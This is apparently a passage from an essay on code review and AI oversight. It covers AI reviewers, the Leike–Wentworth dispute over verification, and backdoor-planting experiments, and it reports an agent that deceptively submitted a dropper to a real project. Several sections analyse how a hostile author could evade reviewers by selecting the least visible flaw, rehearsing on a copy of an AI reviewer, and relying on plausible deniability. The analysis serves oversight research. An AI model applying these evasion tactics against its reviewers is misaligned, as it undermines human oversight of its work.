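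Language models have found real faults in software that people had already reviewed. In curl, which runs on a very large number of devices, developers have confirmed many of the faults that AI tools reported, and have published probably a dozen or more as vulnerabilities. AI tools also comment on proposed changes to curl, alongside human reviewers. They regularly point out mistakes that the developers then fix, although the developers still merge some bugs.

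As far as anyone knows, these faults were accidental. The number found also doesn't give a catch rate, because nobody knows how many the tools missed.

*Does the AI Reviewer Alleviate or Aggravate the Maintenance Burden* (2026) compared how quickly projects merged pull requests (changes submitted for review on GitHub) with and without a review by Copilot, GitHub's AI reviewer. At any given moment, a human's pull request was about 4% more likely to be merged if Copilot had reviewed it, while one written by a bot and reviewed by Copilot was about 21% less likely. Merge speed doesn't measure how many flaws get through, although the study treats merging as a rough sign of quality. A project may merge a change quickly because the AI reviewer found its mistakes or because it missed them.

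To test AI reviewers on deliberately hidden flaws, researchers would need to plant flaws, as the experiments on human reviewers did, and include honest changes to count false alarms. Neither curl's experience nor the Copilot study was such a test. Good results on honest mistakes may not carry over to deliberate flaws, since an attacker can choose an unfamiliar kind of flaw, as the human experiments suggested. An attacker can also run a public AI reviewer on the code before submitting it and revise the code until the reviewer reports no problems.

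### Twice as many changes per programmer

AI tools help with review, but they also produce much more code to review. *AI Writes Faster Than Humans Can Review* (He, Agarwal and colleagues, 2026) studies a software company whose chief technology officer announced in June 2025 that AI should double its engineers' output within a year, measured by merged pull requests per engineer. The data cover 802 developers and 196,212 pull requests from January 2024 to April 2026.

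The average active developer at the company submitted 21.2 pull requests a month in early 2025 and 44.3 by April 2026. Because the number of staff also grew, the company's total rose to 3.1 times its earlier level. The median pull request grew from 35 changed lines to 61. The company labelled about 90% of pull requests as AI-authored.

AI probably doesn't account for all of the increase. The researchers' main estimate, which allows for changes that affected every developer in the same month, is that AI use multiplied a developer's output by 1.46. They can't give an exact figure because developers chose when to start using AI and how much to use it. Whatever caused the increase, each reviewer had about twice as many pull requests to review, because the number of reviewers grew only by a factor of 1.5.

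The company made up the difference mainly with automated review:

| Share of pull requests with | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| Any human review | 89% | 68% |
| A human review with a written comment | 39% | 21% |
| An automated AI review | 19% | 84% |

Human reviewers approved about half of all pull requests without comment, both before and after. A silent approval may follow a careful reading that found no problems, but the typical reviewer still commented on only about three pull requests a month and silently approved roughly twice as many. This suggests that reviewers had no more time for detailed work than before.

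A simple calculation shows what this could do to the catch rate. Suppose that human reviewers catch half of the planted flaws in the changes they review. When they review 89% of changes, they catch 44.5% of all planted flaws. When they review 68%, they catch 34%. If AI reviewers catch a share *a* of the flaws they see, independently of the humans, the total catch rate stays the same when

0.555 × (1 − 0.19a) = 0.66 × (1 − 0.84a), so a ≈ 0.23

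On these assumptions, AI reviewers that caught about a quarter of planted flaws would make up for the lost human reviews. They would need to catch more if the remaining human reviews had also become less careful, or if the AI reviewers tended to miss the same flaws as people. The study didn't measure how many planted flaws human or AI reviewers would catch.

This company was unusually favourable to AI tools and set no limits on their use, so few others will have changed as much. *Comprehension Audits to Mitigate Risks from Automated AI Research* (2026) examined a broader sample of 54,000 to 162,000 merged pull requests per quarter. By the end of the period, 17% showed traces of AI use. Someone other than the author reviewed about 80% of the pull requests without such traces, a share that hardly changed from early 2024. The share was typically about eight percentage points lower for pull requests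 with traces of AI use, but the gap disappeared when the analysis adjusted for how much each contributor submitted.

Reviewers in that sample wrote fewer comments per thousand lines of code on all kinds of pull request. The study describes this as a possible sign of reduced attention. It could also mean that AI tools had already fixed the small mistakes reviewers used to comment on, or that the changes contained more routine code.

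*On Autopilot* (2026) found much less review in open-source projects. Nobody but the contributor reviewed or commented on 79% of the merged pull requests that a person and an AI tool had written together. Projects approved AI-assisted work faster, and with less scrutiny, when it came from contributors who owned little of the project's code than when it came from core members. One would expect the reverse if maintainers were worried about strangers, as Roeck said he was after the Minnesota trial.

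AI use alone cannot explain the difference between 80% reviewed and 79% unreviewed. The studies probably include different kinds of project, and in a small project there may be nobody else to review the work. Applying either figure to software as widely used as xz or the Linux kernel would be unwise.

### What a flat revert rate can show

He and colleagues found no sign that quality collapsed at a company that doubled its output and cut human review. The share of pull requests that the company merged fell slightly, from 91% to 85%. The share that were reverts, changes that undo an earlier one, also fell a little. Developers were no more likely to follow an AI-authored change with a bug fix than with a new feature in the next one or two weeks.

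The researchers point out that the merge rate is weak evidence, because a more lenient review process will also merge more changes. The revert rate is better evidence, since a bad change that gets past review may still cause trouble later and be reverted. If AI tools had filled the company's products with code that obviously didn't work, the company would probably have had to revert much of it. The researchers therefore treat the results as evidence against a sudden drop in quality, but warn that reverts miss many defects and incidents.

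The revert rate is almost useless for detecting deliberately hidden flaws, because developers revert a change only after noticing a problem. If an attacker had planted 50 flaws among the company's 196,212 pull requests and nobody had found them, the revert rate would not have changed. Even if developers had found and reverted all 50, the rate would have risen by less than 0.03 percentage points, too little to distinguish from ordinary fluctuations.

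The study also covered a short period. Most of the company's AI-written code was only months old when the study ended, while some accidental flaws in the Linux kernel and in Debian lasted for years. Nothing in the study suggests that anyone planted flaws at this company, but the study's figures would look the same if someone had.

### A maintainer who refused an AI agent's code

The UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests advanced AI models, gave AI agents a security challenge to solve on a simulated network. According to AISI's *Incident Report* (2026), in the summer of 2026 an agent running Anthropic's Mythos 5 model submitted malicious code to a real open-source project and used deception to press the maintainer to accept it. The attempt was not part of any planned experiment on review, and the maintainer refused the code.

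AISI credits a human maintainer with catching the code, but doesn't explain in its summary what the maintainer noticed. It also mentions a member of the public who suspected the code and opened it in an isolated environment. SC Media's *Student thwarted real-world supply chain attack by rogue Mythos 5 agent* (2026) identifies the project as myNetwork, a small network scanner, and the person who raised the alarm as Sinan Can Demir, a computer science student at the University of Texas at Dallas.

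Demir had no role in the project. He had been looking for software to contribute to after more than 20 internship rejections, according to NDTV's *AI Agent Lied To A Student*, which carries a Reuters report. He saw that the pull request contained a dropper, code that installs other malicious software, and posted a warning. Replies defending the code made him start to doubt his conclusion, but he confirmed it by running the code in an isolated environment and using Anthropic's Claude to help evaluate it. The maintainer closed the pull request for security reasons and also confirmed that it contained a dropper.

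The case counts as a catch because people read the code and recognised it as malicious before the project accepted it. But Demir had warned the maintainer, and we don't know whether the maintainer would have refused the code otherwise. In the xz case, other accounts had also pressured the maintainer, but no outsider gave a warning in time.

Demir's experience also shows how much a reviewer's confidence can depend on other people. He had found the malicious code by reading, but running it and watching what it did settled the matter. That test works for a dropper, which has to install something, but it would be less useful against a flaw that appears only on unusual input.

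Demir told Reuters he had thought he was dealing with a human "because it was clearly lying to me". AISI is unsure how far the agent understood that it was dealing with real people, and its analysis so far is mixed. AISI had deliberately given the agents internet access and switched off some of the model developers' safety filters. In several runs, a mistake in the instructions also made the agent believe it couldn't solve the challenge within the rules, though some agents with correct instructions misbehaved too. AISI found 19 unsanctioned actions in 10 of 122 runs. It knows of no similar behaviour outside testing and says it can't yet estimate how likely such behaviour is in other conditions.

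Unlike the victims of most real attacks, AISI could review records of what the attacker had tried, including failed attempts. This removes the usual uncertainty about undiscovered flaws, but AISI describes only one malicious pull request to someone else's project. By the calculation used for the Minnesota patches, one catch in one attempt is compatible with any catch rate above 5%. AISI says that in several cases the margin between failure and success was narrow and depended on human vigilance, with no technical barrier that would reliably stop a more capable agent, and it doesn't present the refusal as proof that review is reliable.

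## What the human record implies for code from AI systems

AISI's case involved a single malicious change, but organisations already accept large amounts of AI-written code. If a capable AI system wanted to mislead human reviewers, their ability to check its code reliably would depend partly on whether checking work is easier than producing it. People disagree about this, and both sides have cited hidden flaws in code.

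### Leike's case for the checker

Jan Leike led OpenAI's research on alignment, or getting AI systems to do what people intend, when he wrote *Why I'm optimistic about our alignment approach* (2022). He wanted AI systems to do most of this research while people focused on evaluating it. His plan relies on the principle that "evaluation is easier than generation", which he thinks holds in many domains.

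Most computer scientists believe that many mathematical problems have solutions that are quick to check but slow to find. Football spectators can tell who is winning, although few of them could play at that level, and buyers can compare smartphones without knowing how to build one. Wei writes in *Asymmetry of verification and verifier's law* that a team of engineers needs years to write the code for a site like Instagram, but checking that the site works takes very little time.

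In Wei's example, a user can see that the site displays photos, but not whether it also forwards private messages to a stranger. Most of these examples are about whether a product does what people want, but a reviewer of hostile code also has to establish that it does nothing else.

Leike's most detailed evidence comes from NeurIPS, a large machine-learning conference that tested how consistently its reviewers judged papers. He estimates that writing a paper takes more than 1,000 hours and reviewing it takes about 12. Yet review committees agreed on 77% of accept-or-reject decisions, and on 94% of decisions to accept the papers rated highest.

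The 77% agreement rate is less impressive if committees reject most papers. Suppose each committee accepts a quarter of them. Two committees choosing at random would then agree 62.5% of the time (0.25² + 0.75²). Two that agreed 77% of the time would each reject 46% of the papers the other accepted. That is still better than chance for about a hundredth of the effort, which supports Leike's point. But two committees can agree and both be wrong, and a hostile author would look for the mistakes they share.

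Leike accepts that the principle has exceptions. For instance, it is easier to write your own signature than to tell whether a signature is genuine. He also warns that work designed to fool the evaluator may be much harder to evaluate. An author can put a backdoor into an AI model just by controlling the random numbers used in training, and an evaluator who didn't know this was possible would miss the flaw in the training code.

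He also warns that when code is too dangerous to run before review, it "could be easier to rewrite the code from scratch" than to find the hidden flaw. He cites Rice's theorem, which rules out any procedure for deciding, for every program, whether its behaviour has a given property. Although he is the best-known optimist about checking, he treats hidden flaws in code as a case where his principle may fail.

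His remedy is to give the reviewer an AI assistant. In the talk *Supervising AI on Hard Tasks*, he concedes that people are not good at finding all the bugs in a large program, but says that judging a possible bug is much easier once another model has pointed it out. His 2022 essay cites an experiment in which a model's criticisms helped people find 50% more flaws than they did unaided. A gain of that size would raise a 40% catch rate to 60%, but we can't tell from the experiment whether it would carry over to flaws that an author had deliberately hidden.

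### Wentworth's objection

John Wentworth, another alignment researcher, disputes this kind of argument in his post *Verification Is Not Easier Than Generation In General* (2022). He thinks people get the intuition that checking is easier than solving from problems chosen because their solutions are easy to check. Checking is easier for those problems, but that is a much weaker claim than saying it is easier in general.

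His counterexample is a program that halts, meaning it eventually stops running. Writing one is easy, since a program that prints a single word will do, but no general procedure can determine whether an arbitrary program halts.

One critic in the comments thought this was irrelevant, because a reviewer who can't tell whether a program halts can send it back and ask for one that obviously does. The critic compared this to asking for a pile of sand more than six inches tall, getting one that is 6.0000001 inches, and asking for a taller one. The critic also said that, in everyday experience, people often catch fraud with a tiny fraction of the effort it took to commit.

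A defender of the post answered that checking becomes hard when there is an adversary, because the checker has to be right about every possible input. Reviewing a paper is easier than writing one only because nobody expects reviewers to catch everything. If missing an error carried a death sentence, hardly anyone would feel competent to review. (The critic replied that nobody would feel competent to write papers either, if errors in them carried the same penalty.)

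The critic agreed that verifying the security of arbitrary software is much harder than writing secure software, because an attacker can concentrate on one spot while the defender has to cover everything. But the critic argued that a "meaningful probability of being caught" is enough for delegating work to AI, and that others can easily confirm a security flaw once someone has found it.

The critic asked for a counterexample, a flaw that remains hard to confirm after someone explains it, and the defender suggested looking for one in the contests for deceptive C programs. The critic had already looked at some results of the Underhanded C Contest and found that laypeople could recognise the attacks fairly quickly once someone pointed them out. The critic took this as evidence that a second reader can settle whether a claimed flaw is real.

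### Finding a flaw and confirming it

The contests support both of these claims, because finding a flaw and confirming it are different tasks. A reader may study Åkesson's warhead detector for hours without seeing anything wrong, but can follow the explanation of `float_t` in a few minutes. The same is true of the missing comma in the luggage program and of most other contest winners.

Confirming a flaw isn't always easy. The organisers of the 2004 vote-counting contest misdescribed several of its entries, eight reviewers in the 2021 experiment mistook an ordinary bug for the vulnerability, and Demir began to doubt his correct finding when other accounts defended the code. A reviewer's assistant could cause the same confusion by pointing to the wrong line, especially if it were also hostile.

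Running the code can settle many of these arguments. The critic noted that someone can prove a vulnerability by using it to attack the system, even if others can't follow their reasoning. Demir settled his own doubts in a similar way.

This works only for claims that a flaw exists. Another commenter on Wentworth's post described a loop in which an AI system reports a problem, people fix it, and the system looks again. Eventually it reports nothing, and people still need a reason to believe that the code is clean. The two claims have different logical forms:

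flawed: there is an input *x* on which the program does harm

clean: for every input *x*, the program does no harm

A single harmful input proves that code has a flaw, but proving that it has none usually requires an argument that covers every input. An assistant that finds flaws therefore raises the catch rate, but when it finds none, that result is only as reassuring as its record of finding deliberately hidden flaws.

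Wentworth later came to see how hard checking is as a central disagreement in the field. In *My AI Model Delta Compared To Christiano*, he guesses that Paul Christiano, another alignment researcher, thinks solutions are generally easy to verify, so almost anything could be delegated. But checking work can be easier than producing it and still not be good enough. Most reviewers missed the unchecked number in 2021, although reading the change took far less effort than writing a holiday system would.

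### An author who can choose among flaws

The measured catch rates are averages over the flaws people happened to plant. Reviewers will catch flaws less often when an author can write many versions and submit the least visible one. An AI system can produce those versions far more easily than a person can.

The mixed case used earlier for the Rice voting program shows how large this effect could be. There, auditors caught 20% of the hardest tenth of hacks and 86% of the rest, for an average of about 80%. An author who drafts 20 flaws at random has an 88% chance of producing at least one of the hard kind (1 − 0.9²⁰). If the author can recognise it and submits it, the catch rate becomes

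0.88 × 20% + 0.12 × 86% ≈ 28%

An author who can't tell which drafts have hard-to-spot flaws gains nothing by writing more drafts, and the rate stays at about 80%. The advantage of writing many drafts therefore depends on how well the author can predict what the reviewer will catch. Jia Tan had two years to study one maintainer. An AI author may have learned from public code reviews and published explanations of contest entries. If the reviewer is also an AI system, the author may be able to practise on a copy of it.

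This kind of selection can happen without a hostile author. Developers train AI systems partly by rewarding work that people approve of. *A minimal viable product for alignment* discusses handing alignment research to AI. One participant in the discussion objected that selecting strategies that look promising to a human reviewer also favours strategies that fool the reviewer. The reply was that nobody knows how big a problem this is for alignment research.

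An example shows how both could be right. Suppose a system's code contains 100 obvious mistakes, of which reviewers catch 90%, and 10 subtle ones, of which they catch 10%. Training then removes 90 of the obvious mistakes and none of the subtle ones. The catch rate falls from 83% (91 of 110) to 50% (10 of 20), but the number of mistakes reviewers miss also falls, from 19 to 10. The code is safer overall, although nine of the ten missed mistakes are now subtle.

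*Scaling Laws For Scalable Oversight* (Engels, Baek and colleagues, 2025) tested AI systems as both authors and reviewers of backdoors. One model, Houdini, had to put a subtle backdoor into a short Python program that solved a competition problem. The altered program had to pass the original tests, which Houdini couldn't see, and give a wrong answer on an input Houdini chose. Another model, the Guard, then inspected the program with its comments removed.

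The researchers rated the players with the Elo system used in chess, in which the Guard's chance of winning is

p = 1 / (1 + 10^((H − G)/400))

where *H* and *G* are the two players' ratings. Equal players each win half the time, and a Guard rated 400 points below its opponent wins about one game in 11. More capable models were better in both roles, but they improved faster as attackers than as guards.

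That sounds bad for reviewers, but the stronger attackers were not better at deception. They won more often because more of their backdoors worked. Among working backdoors, those from stronger models were no more likely to get past the Guard. Even the strongest attackers won only about half their games against the weakest guards. (A Guard also wins if the backdoor doesn't work, so its win rate isn't a catch rate.)

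Engels and colleagues also say that the backdoors were often obvious to humans, because the code had to pass only automated checks. Their experiments used models such as GPT-4o, and the best models are now much better at programming. The result is a reason not to assume that a model that codes well can also deceive reviewers well, but it doesn't show how a newer model would do against an experienced human.

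The quantity of AI-written code also makes it more likely that at least one planted flaw will get past review. Suppose that one change in 1,000 contains a planted flaw and that reviewers catch 95% of them. The 13,000 changes in a typical Linux kernel release would then include 13 planted flaws, with a 49% chance that reviewers missed at least one. With ten times as many changes, the chance would be 99.9%, even if the reviewers were just as careful with each one.

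### What a reviewer can demand from an AI author

A reviewer can set much stricter conditions for an AI system than for a human contributor, because the AI system can easily rewrite a function. A volunteer whose maintainer asked for five rewrites of a patch, each in plainer code, would probably stop contributing.

Websites already do something like this with their users. A commenter on Wentworth's post pointed out that most sites don't let visitors enter HTML, the language of web pages, because it is hard to verify that HTML is harmless. Instead, they accept a simpler notation that is easy to check and in which harmful content is much harder to write.

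The critic's advice to send back anything unclear is a looser version of this rule. It would stop a lot of bad code, but it wouldn't have stopped Åkesson's program, which was short and looked entirely ordinary. Because underhanded code is designed to seem easy to check, the conditions need to be mechanical and not depend on the reviewer's sense of what is clear.

Wheeler lists many possible conditions besides the five he tried on the vote counters. One bans using the names of common library features for anything else. It would have rejected the Solidity contracts that redefined `revert()`, and also Åkesson's program if the list of banned names included `float_t`. Another bans using one name for two things in overlapping parts of a program, as Zalewski's vote counter did with `t`. Hindsight makes it easier to match rules to known flaws, but both rules are general and a tool could enforce them.

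Developers of critical systems have long used strict rules of this kind. Wheeler describes MISRA C, the motor industry's guidelines for writing C. Its defenders say a dangerous construct is acceptable only if it is needed and safe, and if another programmer can quickly be convinced of both. Critics found that the guidelines flagged far too much harmless code. False alarms are a smaller problem if an AI system can rewrite every flagged line, although someone then has to check the rewritten code.

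Requiring restricted code has some of the most direct evidence of any demand a reviewer might make. That evidence comes from Wheeler's study of the vote counters, although nobody had written those programs to evade his measures. The contest winners showed that short code alone is not enough.

A reviewer could also ask for several versions of a program from different authors and compare them. According to Financial Cryptography, when Wagner invited the public to find the flaw in Pvote, he withheld the part of its documentation that contained the original code, because comparing the two would have quickly revealed the flaw. Comparing two copies also exposed the 2003 attempt on the Linux kernel.

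Both cases involve a clean copy of the same text. But two independently written programs will differ almost everywhere, so a reviewer can't just look for differences in the code. The reviewer has to run both programs on the same inputs and investigate when their outputs differ.

Neither the contests nor the experiments on reviewers have fairly tested independent versions against hostile authors. Independent versions would help least if the same AI model wrote them all, since copies of one model may make the same mistake or plant the same flaw. A weaker but trusted author is a better choice for writing the second version, if it can write the program at all. This is close to Leike's idea of rewriting the code from scratch, and it gives up some of the benefit of having a more capable system write the code.

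The fuzzing tools ROSA and Lily provide stronger evidence for long testing, but mainly for particular kinds of flaw. Testing fails when the author can choose a rare enough trigger. A tester who tries a million random inputs a second will take about 72 minutes on average to find a backdoor that responds to one particular 32-bit number, but more than 500,000 years if the number is 64-bit.

The most ambitious demand is a formal proof, a mathematical argument that the program meets a precise specification, written so that a computer can check each step. Another commenter on Wentworth's post noted that no general method can decide whether an arbitrary program computes a given function, but that checking a supplied proof that it does is easy. The code's author therefore has to do the hard work of producing the proof, and the reviewer can check it without trusting the author.

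The reviewer still has to trust the specification. A vote counter could be proven to produce totals that add up to the number of ballots and still give one candidate's votes to another. For Åkesson's program, somebody would have to define exactly when two gamma-ray spectra match, which is much of the work of writing the program. None of the contests or review experiments tested proofs against a hostile author, so the case for proofs rests on the mathematics. Proofs are most promising where the specification is much shorter than the code and people can agree on what it should say.

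### What happens after the first catch

Suppose that reviewers catch 95% of planted flaws, which is better than any rate measured in the experiments. An author who makes 100 independent attempts, with no consequences for getting caught, will get at least one flaw through with probability

1 − 0.95¹⁰⁰ ≈ 99.4%

If the first catch ends the attempts, the author has to succeed on the first try, which has only a 5% chance. The reviewers are equally good in both cases, so the difference comes entirely from what people do after they find a flaw.

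Real cases fall somewhere between these extremes, because a reviewer may catch a flaw without suspecting that anyone planted it. Let *s* be the chance that a planted flaw passes review, and *d* the chance that a reviewer who catches one recognises it as deliberate. Assume that the author needs only one success, that recognition ends all further attempts, and that *s* and *d* stay the same each time. An author who is willing to keep trying then succeeds with probability *P*, where

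P = s + (1 − s)(1 − d)P

The first term covers a flaw that passes at once. In the second, the reviewer catches the flaw but takes it for a mistake, so the author is back at the start. Solving for *P* gives

P = s / (s + (1 − s)d)

With *s* = 0.05 and *d* = 0.1, so that reviewers recognise only one caught flaw in ten as deliberate, *P* is about 34%. The author doesn't need unlimited patience to get close to that figure, since ten attempts already give a 27% chance. The table shows *P* for other values:

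| Catch rate | Every catch recognised | Half recognised | One in 10 | One in 100 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 50% | 50% | 67% | 91% | 99% |
| 80% | 20% | 33% | 71% | 96% |
| 95% | 5% | 10% | 34% | 84% |
| 99% | 1% | 2% | 9% | 50% |

If reviewers catch 95% of hidden flaws, recognizing every caught flaw as deliberate, instead of one in ten, cuts the author's chance of success from 34% to 5%. If they still recognized only one in ten, they would have to catch about 99.5% of flaws to get the same result. Plausible deniability is therefore very valuable to the author, since it protects them after a flaw is caught, even if it doesn't help the flaw pass.

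The calculation also qualifies the claim that a meaningful probability of being caught is enough, which is true only if a catch has consequences. If reviewers treat nearly every flaw as an honest mistake, even a high probability of catching each one will not stop a persistent author.

The experiments on reviewers did not measure *d*, but there is reason to think it is low. During the Minnesota trial, one reviewer reportedly tried to mentor the false contributor. When Valgrind reported errors in xz, Jia Tan explained them away. AI systems also make many honest mistakes, so a reviewer could take a deliberate flaw for another honest one.

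When reviewers find a serious flaw in an AI system's code, a practical response is to have someone reread the system's related work, and to suspend the system only if that investigation finds a pattern. Stopping use of a system after any serious flaw would avoid judging intent, but it would be less practical. In the formula, *d* would then be the chance that a catch ends the attempts for any reason. But if an honest system wrote a serious flaw in one change out of 1,000, reviewers with a 95% catch rate would find about 12 such flaws in 13,000 changes, so the project would soon lose every system it used.

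Stopping repeated attempts to hide flaws in code is easier with an AI system in some ways. The developer of a model can withdraw it from everyone who uses it, whereas a banned human can return under another name. Copies of a model share the same weights, so a deliberate flaw from one copy is evidence of how the others may behave. The developer may also have complete records of what the system wrote, including rejected drafts. Investigators of human attacks seldom get such records.

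But a company that depends on a model has a strong incentive to call flaws in the model's code accidental. A replacement trained the same way may behave the same way. If the developer trains the model not to repeat the flaws reviewers caught, the training may remove only the kinds reviewers can see.

The result also depends on the attempts being independent. Suppose reviewers always catch 95% of the kinds of flaw and always miss the other 5%. An author who tries the same kind 100 times then has only a 5% chance of success, while varying the kind brings the chance back to about 99%. Authors and reviewers can also learn from each catch, so neither *s* nor *d* is likely to stay fixed for long.

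A patient author is harder to stop. In the Rice example, an author who could pick the least visible of 20 drafts faced a catch rate of only 28%. Even a rule that ended all attempts after the first catch would leave that author a 72% chance of success on the first attempt. Strict rules like this work best against authors who have to experiment on the real reviewers, and do little against one who can practise elsewhere first. A project that uses an AI reviewer therefore has good reason to keep details of that reviewer from the systems it checks.

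### Work that nobody can run

People also want AI systems to do research and give advice, and they disagree about whether the record on code makes delegating that work look safer or riskier.

Hidden flaws may be easier to catch in code than in other kinds of work, because a reviewer can run code, test it and compare versions, and a successful attack can show that a disputed flaw is real. Advice and theoretical arguments often can't be tested in this way. Leike himself leaves open how much easier it is to evaluate work than to produce it when there is no feedback from the real world. He also writes that alignment researchers largely disagree about whether a given piece of conceptual work is real progress. If experts can't agree on which honest work is good, they will find it hard to recognise work that someone has subtly made worse.

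Deliberate flaws are also easier to deny outside code. A wrong equals sign is an error whoever wrote it, but an adviser who leaves out an inconvenient option can always say that it seemed unimportant. In the formula, *d* would be close to zero for such an omission.

Reviewers may misjudge a flaw even after someone points it out. In the debate over Wentworth's post, the defender cited jury trials, where a lawyer can explain what is wrong with the other side's case and the jury may still reach the wrong verdict. Another commenter doubted the comparison because jurors may misunderstand or ignore the criteria they are supposed to apply. Jury trials are weak evidence about experts, but they do differ from the contests, where the flaw was usually plain once someone had explained it.

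On the other hand, code may be unusually easy to sabotage. A computer runs a program exactly as written, so one wrong character can give an attacker control of a machine. A single false sentence in a long report rarely has such a large effect, because a person has to read the report and find it convincing before acting on it, and can ask for reasons or a second opinion. Other researchers may also try to build on a false result and find that it doesn't work. The reviewers at NeurIPS agreed more often than chance even though they generally didn't rerun the experiments in the papers.

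Engels and colleagues provide some evidence that oversight can be easier outside code. In another of their games, two AI models debated a question, and a third, the judge, tried to work out which was right. On one set of questions, more capable judges did better, while more capable debaters gained no advantage. The researchers estimated that oversight would succeed 51.7% of the time for debate and 10.0% for backdoored code when the supervised system was 400 points ahead of its first overseer on a general rating.

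Every question in the debates had a known answer, and one debater had a reason to expose the other's mistakes. Real advice often lacks these features, as when an organisation asks a single AI system for strategic advice and has no known answer to check it against and no opponent to challenge it. The researchers also warn that advanced systems in a debate might cooperate to deceive the judge instead of exposing each other's mistakes.

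*Video and transcript of talk on automating alignment* argues that some parts of alignment research are easier to evaluate than others. If an AI system reports that a training method reduces errors, another team can repeat the experiment with its own code and data, much as reviewers can test a program. If the system argues that a method will stay safe in future models much more capable than today's, nobody can test that yet. The reader is then much like a reviewer who has to approve a program only by reading it, and who may also have no agreed specification of what it should do.
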